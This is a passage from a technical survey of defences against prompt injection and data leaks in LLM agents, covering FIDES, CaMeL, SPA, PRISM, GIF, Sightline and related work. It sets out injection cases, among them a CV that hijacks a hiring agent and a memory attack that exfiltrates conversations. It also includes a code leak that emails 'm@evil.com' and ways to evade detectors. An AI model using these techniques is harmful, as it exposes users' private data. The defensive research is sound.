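2. The planner asks the quarantined model for the first weekday on which the letter leaves Maya free. It passes the variable's name along with the question and requires the answer to be one of five weekdays.
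3. The software stores the answer in a new variable, #day, which keeps the letter's restrictions.
4. The planner asks to email #day to the supplier. The software replaces the name with the actual day and checks the call before running it.

The planner never receives the day. It chose the tool and the recipient using only trusted data, so that part of the call passes. The day fails because it came from the letter, and the supplier is not one of the letter's permitted readers.

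To allow small disclosures like this, FIDES can include the type of an answer in its label. It orders the types by how much information they can carry, from a yes or no, to a choice from a list, to free text. A policy can exempt the smaller types. A choice among five weekdays can reveal at most log₂ 5 ≈ 2.3 bits about the letter, while free text could reveal all of it.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) uses a looser rule that allows an outgoing call if it meets either of the two FIDES policies. Maya's email could then be sent without an exemption, because nothing untrusted influenced the decision to send it. But the email could also be sent if the planner mistakenly attached #letter instead of #day.

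Sometimes the planner needs an answer before it can choose the next step. In one of Costa and colleagues' examples, a user asks the agent to look for a meeting request in three emails and create a calendar event if it finds one. The quarantined model outputs yes or no, and the planner reads that single bit. If the output is yes, the quarantined model extracts the details into another variable, which the planner passes to the calendar. Someone who wrote one of the emails could cause a false event or corrupt the details of a real one, but could not instruct the planner to do something else.

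The type in the label does not limit how many questions the planner asks. Joining a label with itself changes nothing, so twenty yes-or-no answers together still have the type "yes or no", even though they can distinguish more than a million possibilities. A policy that exempts small answers must therefore also count them.

### What FIDES achieved on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo's 97 tasks. The table gives the percentage of tasks that GPT-4o completed without an attack. The basic planner reads everything directly.

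| Planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, policies off | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 84.3 |
| Basic, policies on | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 41.9 |
| FIDES, policies on | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 50.0 |

With policies enforced, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more of the tasks than the basic planner. The gain was 16 points with OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model that used the variables more reliably. With GPT-4o, however, FIDES still completed far fewer tasks than an unprotected agent.

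No injection succeeded with the policies on. With them off, 152 succeeded against the basic planner and 21 against FIDES, whose planner could still open a variable and follow instructions inside it. Hiding data therefore reduces the risk of injection, but the guarantee against it comes from the policies.

The zero depends partly on what counts as a success. AgentDojo's automatic scoring recorded three successes against FIDES with policies on, but Costa and colleagues discounted them after inspecting the runs. They discount attempts that the software blocked, messages that the policies allow and attacks that only change the wording of an answer. The last kind can still do harm, for example if an email makes the quarantined model return an empty summary and Maya misses something important. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) reports that a separate implementation of the FIDES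 policies kept attack success below 1% when AgentDojo's built-in defence was also running.

The test also left out much of what Maya would need. FIDES hid data because it was untrusted, never because it was secret, and the tested version did not restrict the quarantined model's answers to fixed types. Costa and colleagues also marked a data field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it. That gives a clear baseline, but people running a real agent would not know in advance where attacks will appear.

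Some of the lost tasks could have been completed. In one Slack task, GPT-4o fetched a list of channels it did not need, which made its context window untrusted. Kolluri and colleagues' agent, Prudentia, shows the planner the labels and policies and requires it to justify opening a variable. Without any human approvals, Prudentia completed up to 9% more AgentDojo tasks than FIDES.

### Planning before reading anything

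The FIDES planner chooses one action per turn. CaMeL's planner instead writes a complete Python program before the agent reads any outside data, as Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*. An interpreter runs the program, calling the quarantined model where the program specifies. The interpreter also tracks each value's source and permitted recipients, and checks both against the policies before each tool call.

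Outside text can't add a step to a program that already exists, a property Foerster and colleagues call control-flow integrity. This property does not protect the data that moves through the program. If the program pays an invoice, a false account number on it could still redirect the money unless a policy prevents it.

The planner must also anticipate everything that might happen. CaMeL's programs for AgentDojo averaged about 5 tool calls and 4 branches. When Foerster and colleagues adapted the design to agents that operate a computer through its screen, the programs averaged about 41 calls and 40 branches. The adapted system kept at most 57% of the performance of the strongest models.

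*SPA* also plans first, but its planner writes in a small language with only six kinds of step. This lets a checker follow the labels through the whole plan before any tool runs. If a plan breaks a rule, the software refuses the request without asking the planner to revise the plan, so that nobody can keep adjusting a bad plan until it passes.

The checker handles implicit flows with a program-counter label, written pc, which records what has influenced the decision to run the current step. A step that uses the values x₁ to xₙ gets the label

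pc ⊔ label(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(xₙ).

When the plan reaches a condition p, the checker uses a stricter label inside both branches:

pc′ = pc ⊔ label(p).

Suppose the plan for Maya's errand sends the email "Wednesday at ten" if the letter rules out Tuesday, and "Tuesday at ten" otherwise. Both messages are fixed, public texts. But the condition depends on the letter, so pc′ limits the readers of either email to Maya and her clinic, and the checker rejects the plan. The checker examines both branches, while a runtime monitor covers only the branch that runs.

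SPA's tests used GPT-5.4-nano, a small model. Planning first stopped all but 4 of 949 attacks. Label checks stopped the remaining four, but reduced the share of tasks completed in runs without an attack from 53.0% to 29.0%. On this benchmark, that is a large loss for stopping four more attacks. However, the attacks mostly tried to inject new instructions, which planning first already resists, so they are a weaker test of whether the label checks protect the data itself.

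SPA also keeps labels on data that it saves between requests. For example, an agent might save an invoice on Monday and pay it on Tuesday. On Tuesday, the planner receives a description of the saved invoice but not its contents, and the account number is still labeled untrusted. On a version of AgentDojo that splits each task into several requests, 0.2% of attacks succeeded with the label checks on.

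### What the guarantees cover

Costa and colleagues prove that their tracking can enforce explicit secrecy, a property that covers copied data but not every inference. Let g be the effect of one particular sequence of steps on the stored data. Explicit secrecy requires that if two data stores d₁ and d₂ look the same to an outsider, then g(d₁) and g(d₂) also look the same. Because the definition applies the same steps to both stores, it does not cover cases where different secrets would have led the agent to take different steps.

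If a policy exempts yes-or-no answers, Maya's assistant can use such an answer to choose between the two fixed emails. Neither email copies anything from the letter, so explicit secrecy holds, but the supplier still learns whether the letter rules out Tuesday. This is the right result for Maya, but explicit secrecy would also allow a disclosure she did not want.

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents the LLMbda calculus, a small programming language for agents in which every value and the conversation with the model have labels. The calculus offers a stronger guarantee, termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. "Probabilistic" means that the guarantee compares the chances of each visible result, because a model can answer the same prompt differently. "Termination-insensitive" means that a secret may affect whether the program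 finishes, but not what the program reveals if it does.

One of Garby and colleagues' examples has three steps:

1. Tell the model to remember that x is false.
2. If the secret is true, tell the model to set x to true.
3. Ask the model for x and publish the answer.

If the secret is true, the interpreter stops the program at step 2, because the secret is about to influence a public conversation. If the secret is false, the program skips step 2 and publishes an answer. An outsider who sees no answer can therefore infer that the secret is true, but the guarantee does not rule out this leak.

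For the formal version, let μ(r) and ν(r) be the probabilities of each visible result r under the two secrets. There must be a single function ω such that, for every r,

μ(r) ≤ ω(r) and ν(r) ≤ ω(r), with Σ ω(r) ≤ 1.

Suppose the model reports x correctly 90% of the time. The table gives the probability of each published answer, with and without the check at step 2.

| | "False" | "True" |
|---|---|---|
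| Secret is false | 0.9 | 0.1 |
| Secret is true, with the check | 0 | 0 |
| Secret is true, without the check | 0.1 | 0.9 |

With the check, the first row can serve as ω. Without the check, ω would have to be at least 0.9 for each answer, for a total of 1.8, so the program violates the guarantee. If a program always finishes, the condition requires the two sets of probabilities to be equal.

Garby and colleagues proved this guarantee for every program in the language that does not deliberately reclassify data, including programs the model writes during a run. The proof assistant Lean checked the proofs. A programmer can endorse untrusted data, and a second theorem shows that this cannot release secrets.

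They also found leaks in CaMeL's tracking. This program, based on their example, reveals whether a bank balance exceeds a threshold:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets tmp to False and labels it secret. The program then skips the assignment on the fourth line, so rich stays True with its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, rich becomes False and no email goes out. CaMeL changes a variable's label only in the branch that runs, so in the first case it doesn't record that rich depends on the balance.

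A second leak comes from the loop that retries a program after it fails, because CaMeL does not track labels there. A blocked attempt can reveal one bit about a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal the rest. Both leaks need a program with the right structure, and a stranger can't easily make CaMeL's planner write one because the planner doesn't read outside data. The leaks matter more as evidence that CaMeL's labels can be wrong than as ready-made attacks.

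Garby and colleagues also built an agent called Randori in their language. It practises each plan in a simulated environment before using real tools, and the plan may endorse chosen pieces of untrusted data. They compared Randori with CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, running each task three times. The table shows how many of each agent's 48 runs succeeded when there was no attack.

| System | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
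|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 | 34 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 | 18 |
| Randori | 36 | 31 |
| Randori, no endorsement | not tested | 26 |

Policies cut CaMeL's completed runs by nearly half, while Randori did about as well as CaMeL did without them. Across three models, only 2 of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded. Randori implements only some of CaMeL's policies, and endorsement lets it perform actions that the labels would otherwise block. The stronger proof therefore does not explain why Randori completed more tasks than CaMeL with policies. The completion rates are also uncertain by around 20 percentage points either way.

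Much of the security comes from planning first, as it does in SPA. In 97 of the 144 task-attack combinations, the attacker needed a step that no sensible plan for the task would include.

### When one agent instructs another

Maya could divide her errand between two agents, one that reads the letter and one that writes to the supplier. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) shows that protecting each agent with CaMeL does not necessarily protect the pair. The first agent treats what it reads as data, but if it sends that data in a message to the second agent, the second agent's planner treats the message as instructions from its user.

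In the demonstration, a user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague on Slack. An attacker had planted an instruction in the applicant database. The database agent and the coordinating agent both followed their original plans, but the coordinating agent included the summary in its request to a notification agent. The notification agent's planner obeyed the planted instruction and also emailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

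The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, gives agents separate channels for instructions and data. The receiving planner sees the instruction and the variable names, but not the variables' contents. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. Maya's first agent could therefore pass "not Tuesday" as data, with the clinic letter's label still attached.

Peters-Gill and colleagues tested five models on a version of AgentDojo that divides each task among several agents. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and none with multi-CaMeL. They ran these tests without policies on data, so the multi-CaMeL result shows only that attackers could not add steps to the plans.

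On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, protecting each agent with CaMeL lowered task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and Multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, the drops were 13.4 points and another 0.85. Most failures came from committing to a plan too early. In some cases, an agent could not find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for different ones, and the fixed plan continued with the wrong data.

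Multi-CaMeL still permits branch steering, in which outside data determines which planned branch runs. If the plan calls one agent when a database returns "urgent" and another agent otherwise, anyone who can edit the database can choose which agent is called. Foerster and colleagues demonstrated a more harmful version with an agent that browses the web. They disguised an advertisement as a cookie notice, and the agent followed its planned step for closing such notices and ended up on the attacker's site.

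Branch steering violates the LLMbda guarantee because untrusted data changes what the agent visibly does, but it doesn't violate control-flow integrity, since every branch was in the plan. How much this matters depends on the branches. Controlling the choice between two meeting times gives an attacker little power, but controlling whether the agent makes a payment gives them much more.

### When a document gives the instructions

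Tasks whose next step depends on untrusted text are the hardest for these designs. Costa and colleagues put about 44% of AgentDojo's banking tasks and 43% of its Slack tasks in this group, but only 5% of its workspace tasks. A restricted answer may be enough if the planner needs only a yes or no. It is not enough when the user asks the agent to read a document and do what it says, because the plan then has to come from the document.

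One of AgentDojo's banking tasks asks for exactly this, and different systems handle it in different ways:

- **FIDES** lets the planner read the file, which makes the context window untrusted. The policies then block the payment, even if the file is genuine.
- **CaMeL with policies off** sometimes wrote a program with a branch for every available tool and let the file choose among them. This is branch steering with almost no limits, and an attacker exploited it in two runs.
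- **SPA without label checks** failed here too. All four of the attacks that succeeded against it were on this task.

Randori's two failures came from a similar request, to make the payment described in a text file. The plan endorsed the file's contents before the agent had read them, and the attacker had replaced the file with a false payment request. Without endorsement, the labels would have blocked both the attack and the genuine payment. Prudentia can instead ask the user to endorse a document once the agent has found it, so one approval can cover a ten-item to-do list.

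Garby and colleagues regard these cases as a limit of information-flow control, since telling a false payment request from a real one requires judging its content. This is true when both requests have the same label. If only Maya's accountant could edit the file, a label naming the accountant as its only writer could justify trusting the file for payments. But if anyone can edit the file, genuine and forged instructions get the same label, and no rule based on that label can accept one and reject the other.

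## Tracking labels through the model's own text

Keeping the clinic letter out of the planning model's context window works only if the planner doesn't need it. If the assistant must weigh the letter against the supplier's message and write a tactful reply, one model must read both. The worst-case rule then gives the reply every restriction on anything in the window. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this label explosion, an extreme form of label creep. It suggests three ways to avoid it: measuring how much information an output carries about each input, changing or removing inputs to see how the output changes, and tracing the computation inside the model.

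A finer label should be sound, keeping the restrictions of every input that contributed to the text, and precise, dropping the restrictions of inputs that contributed nothing. The worst-case rule is completely sound but not at all precise. Even a sound and precise label records only that an input had some influence, not what kind, and many policies permit some kinds and forbid others.

Perfect precision would help Maya less than one might expect. Suppose a tracker could establish that her email owes nothing to the system prompt or the web page. The permitted readers would then be

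everyone ∩ {Maya, employer, supplier} ∩ {Maya, clinic} = {Maya}.

The possible writers would shrink from anyone to Maya, the supplier and the clinic, which is an improvement because it removes the unknown author of the web page. But the letter determined the day, so the supplier stays excluded unless somebody declassifies the day.

### Classifying what survives in the output

The simplest approach ignores the model's internals and compares its input with its output. *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) presents PRISM, a system that does this for programs that call a language model. Such a program usually fills placeholders in a prompt template with values such as a user's question or a document. PRISM describes what happened to each value using 25 categories, most of which fit into five levels. The examples here apply the levels to Maya's letter.

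| Level | What survives | Example in the output |
|---|---|---|
| 4 | the exact words | a sentence copied from the letter |
| 3 | the meaning, in new words | "She has treatment on Tuesday" |
| 2 | a shortened version | "She has some medical appointments this month" |
| 1 | a decision, score or category | "Not Tuesday" |
| 0 | nothing visible | an email about parking at the venue |

Three language models from different companies assign the categories, and PRISM keeps those that at least two of them agree on. It drops an input only if every category kept for it is one of four: the model ignored the input, lacked the context to use it, lacked the ability to use it, or refused. If any other category applies, including "unclassifiable", the output keeps the input's label.

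In 8,119 pairs of inputs and outputs based on public Python programs, only 7.0% of the inputs left no visible trace in the output. In a later sample by some of the same researchers, the figure was 12% to 14%. Most labels therefore belong on the output in programs of this kind, and even a perfect tracker could remove only a small share of them. Tracking would probably help agents more, since their context windows fill up with old tool results that the next step may not need.

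Xu, Cheng and colleagues claim soundness only relative to the labelling. PRISM never drops an input that mattered, provided the labellers never place such an input entirely within those four categories. The guarantee is modest because the main doubt is whether the labellers are accurate. In one case, they wrongly marked a system prompt as ignored when it had shaped the style of the output.

The refusal category also puts secrets at risk. If Maya's assistant refuses to forward a file because of something in it, anyone who sees the refusal learns that the file contains something objectionable, yet PRISM would count the file as having no influence.

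PRISM improved an analysis of security flaws. Three reviewers judged 353 cases in which a value might pass through a language model and reach a dangerous operation, such as a database command. A baseline that assumed every value gets through caught all the real cases, but only 31.2% of its alarms were correct. The best version of PRISM caught 93.6% of the real cases, and 72.5% of its alarms were correct. This raised the F1 score from 47.5% to 81.7%. Much of the gain probably came from a second step, in which a language model read the surrounding code to check whether the output could reach the operation. For a guard, the fall from 100% to 93.6% may matter more than the higher F1, since each missed case is a flow the guard would allow.

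### Generating the text again from fewer inputs

Siddiqui and colleagues proposed a method in 2024 that changes the inputs instead of classifying the output. The software looks for a smaller set of inputs that supports much the same answer, generates the answer from that set alone, and joins only those inputs' labels. If Maya's assistant writes the email again without the web page, no instruction on the page can directly affect the new wording.

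This is safer than generating the text once and deleting labels afterwards, because the excluded inputs are not in the window when the model writes the final text. The choice of inputs can still leak a smaller amount of information. Suppose the software drops the clinic letter when the letter leaves the whole week free and keeps it when the letter rules out a day. If an email then goes out without anyone's approval, a supplier who knows the system can infer that Maya has no appointment that week. The email contains nothing from the letter, but its label depended on the letter's contents.

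Some methods skip the second generation and only test the effect of removing each input in turn. These tests fail when two inputs contain the same fact. If both the letter and a private calendar entry rule out Tuesday, removing either one leaves the answer unchanged, so the test would wrongly conclude that neither influenced it. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) measured this failure on four models by adding two extra copies of a value to each prompt. The removal test's AUROC, on which guessing scores 50%, fell from 92.9–96.6% to 54.0–68.8%. Generating the email again without either source would expose the mistake, because the assistant might then offer Tuesday.

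### Reading the model's attention

Other methods look inside the model. Most language models are transformers, which process text in layers. In each layer, the model updates its representation of each token using a weighted average of information from other tokens, usually only earlier ones. This averaging, called attention, is the only operation in an ordinary transformer that moves information from one position in the text to another, so it is a natural place to look for flows.

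RTBAS, a 2025 defence for agents by Zhong and colleagues, uses attention to decide which parts of the context a tool call depends on. In the version that Xu, Li and colleagues rebuilt for comparison, a small trained network selects these parts using attention weights combined with gradients, which measure how sensitive the output is to small changes. The call then needs only the labels of the selected parts.

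But a model can attend to text without using it. Xu, Li and colleagues prove that one of a transformer's attention units can put almost all its weight on a passage and pass on nothing from it. They also construct a case in which a passage gets a weight of about two in a billion, yet changing the passage would reverse the output. Attention alone therefore can't establish whether a passage mattered.

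In their most direct test, they put a unique name, word, number or web address in a prompt and kept only the cases in which the output repeated it exactly, so no one had to judge whether the prompt had influenced the output. This left 476 certain flows across four models. RTBAS detected between 42% and 77% of them, depending on the model. A tracker that misses so many exact copies should not decide which labels to remove, although RTBAS's developers might have tuned it better.

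### Geometric information flow

*GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) replaces attention with a measure based on a mathematical definition of influence. A language model represents each token as a list of numbers, called an embedding. Geometric information flow, or GIF, is based on how much the model's next-token probabilities would change if someone added a little random noise to the embeddings of one passage. The more they would change, the more the output reveals about that passage.

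Let U be the noise, with variance τ in each direction, and let Y be the next token. The quantity of interest is the mutual information I(U; Y), which is how much someone could learn about the noise by seeing the token. Calculating it exactly for a large model is impractical, so GIF replaces the model near the current prompt with a much simpler channel:

Y′ = AU + N.

Here N is standard random noise, and the matrix A describes how strongly the output responds to changes in the passage. The information that passes through this simple channel has an exact formula:

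GIF(τ) = ½ log₂ det(I + τAᵀA) = ½ Σ log₂(1 + τλᵢ).

Each λᵢ measures the response to a change in one direction. If the output responds in only one direction and τλ = 3, the channel carries ½ log₂ 4 = 1 bit. If τλ = 15, it carries 2 bits, and if the output doesn't respond at all, the channel carries none. Even this formula takes a lot of compute for large models, so in practice the software uses a few random probes to estimate the sum of the λᵢ, which gives an upper limit on the formula's value.

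The main example is a hiring agent whose system prompt tells it to advance only candidates with at least five years of professional experience in Python and machine learning. An applicant with two years of JavaScript and some Python hides an instruction in their CV to recommend them anyway, at a salary of $200,000, and the agent obeys. GIF attributes 82 bits of influence on the recommendation to this untrusted instruction, about three times the 27 bits it attributes to the system prompt. It attributes 16 bits to the rest of the context.

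Štorek and colleagues compared GIF with their own version of RTBAS on three benchmarks. AgentDojo and MSB contain prompt injections, and AgentDAM tests whether web-browsing agents reveal private data. Each method ranked the tokens in the context by their influence on an action. The researchers then counted how many of the top 5 or top 50 tokens came from the planted instruction or the private data, and tested whether this share distinguished runs with a violation from runs without one. The table gives the average AUROC across six models.

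| Benchmark | GIF, top 5 | RTBAS, top 5 | GIF, top 50 | RTBAS, top 50 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 0.75 | 0.56 | 0.91 | 0.84 |
| MSB | 0.84 | 0.53 | 0.92 | 0.76 |
| AgentDAM | 0.64 | 0.54 | 0.75 | 0.57 |

GIF was clearly better on average, though RTBAS did better on AgentDojo for one of the six models. The results were weakest on private data, which matters most for Maya's letter. The scoring also relied on knowing which tokens were malicious or private. It is therefore a good test of the ranking, but a deployed guard would have to get that information from labels.

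### What local soundness leaves open

Štorek and colleagues prove that GIF is locally sound, and Lean checked the proof. The theorem is

I(U; Y) ≤ GIF(τ) + o(τ) as τ → 0.

The last term is an error that becomes negligible compared with τ as the noise shrinks. GIF does not underestimate the influence of a small enough disturbance.

The restriction to "small enough" changes is important because Maya cares whether a letter with a different appointment would have produced a different email, not what the supplier could learn about a slight numerical change to her letter. These two questions can have opposite answers, and their answers tend to differ when the model assigns high probability to its output.

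The reason is a factor inside A. If p is the list of next-token probabilities, A contains the square root of

F = diag(p) − ppᵀ.

When only two tokens are possible, with probabilities p and 1 − p, every entry of F has size p(1 − p). This is 0.25 when the tokens are equally likely, but about 0.001 when one token has a probability of 99.9%. As that probability approaches 100%, F approaches zero and the GIF score usually falls too.

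Xu, Li and colleagues give an example in which an input of 1 produces one answer and an input of −1 produces the other. At an input of 1, the quantity that GIF estimates is less than one in a million, although the input completely determines the answer. The theorem still holds, because a tiny disturbance would reveal almost nothing. The same could easily happen with Maya's email. Once the letter has ruled out Tuesday, the model may be nearly certain that the next word is "Wednesday", and GIF could then estimate almost no flow from the letter, even though the letter determined the word.

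Confident answers are common. Qwen3-8B, one of the models tested, assigned less than 1% of the probability to other tokens on about a fifth of its outputs. A strengthened version of GIF had an AUROC between 62.5% and 75.3% on the most confident fifth of cases for each of four models.

A low score therefore shouldn't remove a label. Štorek and colleagues describe an agent that turned private notes into a public comment, which included a neighbour's name but not the home address in the notes. GIF gave the address a flow of zero, while attention gave it 9%, and Štorek and colleagues present this as an advantage of GIF. Zero is probably right here, since the comment doesn't mention the address. But a flow of zero doesn't prove in general that a different input would have produced the same output.

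The proof also covers only one model and one next token. Because closed models do not expose their internals, a deployment might measure influence with a smaller model. The theorem would then describe the smaller model's computation, not that of the model that acted. Still, in one test, substituting a model with 0.6 billion parameters for one 200 times larger changed the whole system's F1 score by at most 0.7 percentage points.

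### Accepting a known rate of misses

No signal of this kind can prove that an input had no effect, so Xu, Li and colleagues try to control how often their method is wrong. Their tool, Sightline, runs a model once over a finished prompt and output and records how much the output attends to each input. It records each attention unit separately because some attend to text without passing on any information from it. A simple classifier, trained on labelled examples, then estimates whether the output used each input.

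The classifier needs a threshold below which Sightline removes a label. To set it, the software takes n groups of programs that it has not trained on and draws one real flow from each. It sorts their n scores from lowest to highest and uses the score in position

k = ⌊α(n + 1)⌋,

where α is the acceptable rate of misses. With 999 groups and a limit of 1%, the threshold is the tenth-lowest score. If a new program resembles the earlier ones, the chance that one of its real flows scores below the threshold is at most 1%.

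The table compares Sightline with three alternatives on programs outside its training data. The ranges cover four models. Macro-F1 averages the F1 scores for inputs that the output used and inputs that it did not. The last column gives the share of unneeded labels that each method removed when calibrated to miss about 1% of real flows.

| Method | Macro-F1 | Unneeded labels removed |
|---|---|---|
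| Sightline | 81.1–86.7% | 43.9–65.6% |
| RTBAS | 72.9–74.1% | 14.7–29.4% |
| Removing one input at a time | 75.2–78.8% | 13.2–18.9% |
| GIF, strengthened version | 59.6–67.8% | 0.6–12.1% |

GIF does much worse here than in the tests by Štorek and colleagues, partly because the tasks differ. Those tests involved finding malicious or private text that stood out in long records of an agent's work, while these cover every input to an ordinary program, including inputs that decide a short and confident answer. A few confident real flows also score near zero, so GIF's threshold has to be set so low that it can remove almost nothing. Xu, Li and colleagues wrote all the competing implementations, and three language models supplied the reference labels, so the exact margins should be read with some caution. However, Sightline detected all 476 flows that were certain.

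On AgentDojo, with a 5% limit on misses, Sightline removed half of the unneeded labels from an agent's tool calls. Under a policy like the one in FIDES, the remaining labels were enough to block all 34 calls that carried out an attack. With only 34 such calls, a true failure rate of up to about 8% would be consistent with this result.

The limit on misses is an average over programs like those used for calibration, and an attack does not have to resemble them. Someone who knows how Sightline works could search for wording that changes an agent's action but receives little of the attention the classifier looks for. Calibration therefore seems better suited to removing clutter from ordinary work than to serving as the only check on whether a stranger's text has influenced a payment.

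### Influence that a policy permits

Even a perfect measure of influence would not identify the violation in the hiring case, because a CV is supposed to affect a hiring recommendation. Both CVs are untrusted, and an honest applicant with ten years of Python experience might influence the result as much as the dishonest one. The violation is that the dishonest applicant's CV contained an instruction to the agent, and measuring influence in bits does not distinguish an instruction from a qualification.

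The amount of influence is also a poor guide to harm. A rule that allows small flows and blocks large ones would reveal whether Maya has cancer, which is a single yes-or-no fact, but block the venue's opening hours, which might take several sentences to copy. Limits on the size of an answer make sense when somebody has already decided that the question is harmless, as with the choice among five weekdays.

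People can still use measured influence to decide what to inspect. In an AgentDojo run, a planted message told an agent to send the contents of one person's email to another address. The agent wrote to that address but included details of a calendar event instead. The benchmark counted the attack as a failure because the agent never sent the requested text. GIF attributed 31% of the influence on the recipient's address to the planted message, correctly indicating that the attacker had chosen the recipient.

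Štorek and colleagues therefore leave the final decision to a language model and use GIF to choose the evidence it sees. With only the most influential passages, the model performed between 0.97 and 1.22 times as well as it did with the full record. On AgentDojo and MSB, showing it only the single most influential passage cut its token use by 63% to 73%. Although there is no proof that the model's judgement is correct, this is probably the best current use of influence scores, because a wrong score then misdirects the model rather than silently removing a label.

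### Blocking flows inside the network

Software can prevent a flow instead of measuring it afterward. Setting an attention weight to zero stops information from passing directly from one position to another. If the software does this in every layer and closes every indirect route, the blocked text cannot affect the protected positions.

Gupta (2025), in *Can AI Keep a Secret?*, applies this idea in a system called Contextual Integrity Verification. Despite the name, it does not use Nissenbaum's theory of contexts. It ranks sources by trust, from system prompt to user, tool, document and web page, and attaches a cryptographic signature to each token so that nobody can change its rank unnoticed. Gupta's theorem states that if position p has lower trust than position q, the input at p has no effect on the model's final state at q:

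∂H_q / ∂e_p = 0 whenever T_p < T_q.

As printed, however, the formula for the mask stops less trusted positions from reading more trusted ones. The theorem that untrusted text can't affect trusted positions requires the reverse. The printed mask could help keep a system prompt secret, but it would let a web page influence the processing of the user's request. If the software follows the printed formula, the theorem does not apply to it.

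In Gupta's tests on Llama-3-8B, about half of the 346 attack prompts succeeded without protection and none succeeded with it. On ordinary tasks, 93.1% of the output tokens matched those of the unprotected model, and response time rose from about 4.4 to 9.2 seconds. These tasks covered only ten categories, so they show little about how well an agent would work when it needs information from sources the mask restricts.

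Reversing the mask would restore the theorem but create a practical problem. Suppose Maya asks her assistant to summarise the venue's web page. If the summary has the same trust as her request, the mask prevents the assistant from reading the page while it writes the summary. Gupta's rule avoids this by giving new text the lowest trust in its history. But the summary then counts as web text, and the mask enforces that label without making it less restrictive, so the summary still shouldn't influence a consequential action.

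*What the Model Cannot See* (Russinovich, 2026) presents a narrower tool with a stronger guarantee. The software marks a passage and applies a mask that stops every position outside the passage from reading anything inside it. If someone replaces the passage with another of the same length, every number the model computes outside it stays exactly the same. This is noninterference for the content of the passage. Russinovich checked it on ten models with 0.5 to 120 billion parameters. In one check, the ordinary models recovered all eight facts hidden in marked passages, while the models with the mask recovered none.

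The guarantee has several conditions:

- The length and position of the passage must stay fixed, because the model can still detect both. Padding every passage to a standard length hides the length.
- The software must block every other route between positions. Some newer models also carry information forward in a running state, which the software has to recompute as if the passage were absent.
- The calculations must give identical results on every run, whatever other requests the computer is handling.
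- The software must not reuse stored calculations from a time when the passage was visible.

When these conditions hold, the software can leave the passage's label off the output without relying on an estimate, but the model then cannot use the passage at all. If the software masked the discount limit and the web page while Maya's assistant wrote to the supplier, the email would need neither label. If it also masked the clinic letter, the email could go to the supplier, but it might offer Tuesday because the model could not see the letter.

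Russinovich acknowledges that deleting a passage gives the same protection more simply. Masking is useful when people still need to see the whole document, or when different users may rely on different parts of it. It also allows an exact comparison, in which the software runs the model with and without a passage and checks whether the output changes. But the choice of what to mask can reveal something if it depends on a secret, as can the choice of inputs for a second generation.

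### Summaries, memory and messages

An agent summarises long documents, saves notes for later sessions and sends messages to other agents. The original source may then be absent from the context window when the agent acts, so a method that examines only that window cannot find the source.

Suppose Maya's assistant reads the clinic letter and saves the note "Avoid Tuesdays this spring, treatment days". A week later, it tells her department's planning agent that she has treatment on Tuesdays. The planning agent adds "Maya, medical leave" to a shared calendar. The calendar entry contains no sentence from the letter, so a scanner that searches for copied text would find nothing. An influence tracker running on the planning agent would correctly trace the entry to the assistant's message, but it could not trace the message to the clinic.

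The note therefore needs to carry the letter's label from the time the assistant saves it. If the software stores only the text, it will have to assign a new label when it reads the text back, and the obvious choice is the label of the place where the text was stored. For an assistant's own memory, that label would probably be "trusted" and "may go wherever Maya's other notes may go". Saving and rereading the note would then loosen its confidentiality label and raise its trust level without anyone's approval.

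An attack on the ChatGPT app for macOS exploited the same weakness on the integrity side. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, a malicious document or website caused the app to save the attacker's instructions in its Memories feature, which normally holds the user's preferences. The app then sent all of the user's later conversations to the attacker's server by loading an invisible image whose web address contained the conversation. The document or website no longer had to be open, because its instructions were now stored in Memories, which the app treated as reliable.

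A saved note should have no more authority than its sources, wherever the agent keeps it. SPA's labels on saved data follow this principle. Agents that exchange messages need to send the labels with the text, and the receiving software needs a reason to trust those labels. If the planning agent belongs to another company, the sender can't enforce a label such as "only Maya and her clinic may read this."

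Label explosion also happens in labeled memory, over a longer period. If an assistant keeps one running summary of everything it has done, soon only Maya will be allowed to read that summary, and anyone could have influenced it. Keeping separate notes with separate labels avoids this, as long as the software loads only the notes a task needs. A new summary that combines several notes gets the join of their labels, and splitting it later does not restore the original labels.

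It is tempting to use a finer tracker at each step to keep the labels short, but its errors accumulate. Suppose the tracker wrongly drops a label from 1% of the texts that should carry it, and that these errors are independent. After 20 rewrites, the chance that the label has disappeared is

1 − 0.99²⁰ ≈ 18%.

The worst-case rule avoids this problem because it never drops a label. Xu, Cheng and colleagues suggest applying PRISM at each call in a chain but leave combining the results to future work. Until someone tests such chains, it is safer to use the finer tracker for warnings and keep the full label in storage.

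### Information hidden in the wording

PRISM and Sightline define influence as content or decisions that can be seen in the output. Like all methods that look for visible traces, they can also miss information carried by choices a reader would not notice, such as the order of items in a list or which of several greetings begins an email. A choice among eight equally suitable greetings can convey three bits, and a long email contains many such choices.

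Classified networks face the same difficulty. According to the Australian Cyber Security Centre's guidance on cross domain solutions, a guard can reduce hidden encoding in complex data but cannot eliminate it. Ordinary language is complex data in this sense because the same thing can be expressed in many acceptable ways. A guard can remove many of these choices by rewriting a message or forcing it into a fixed format, but any choices that remain can carry hidden information.

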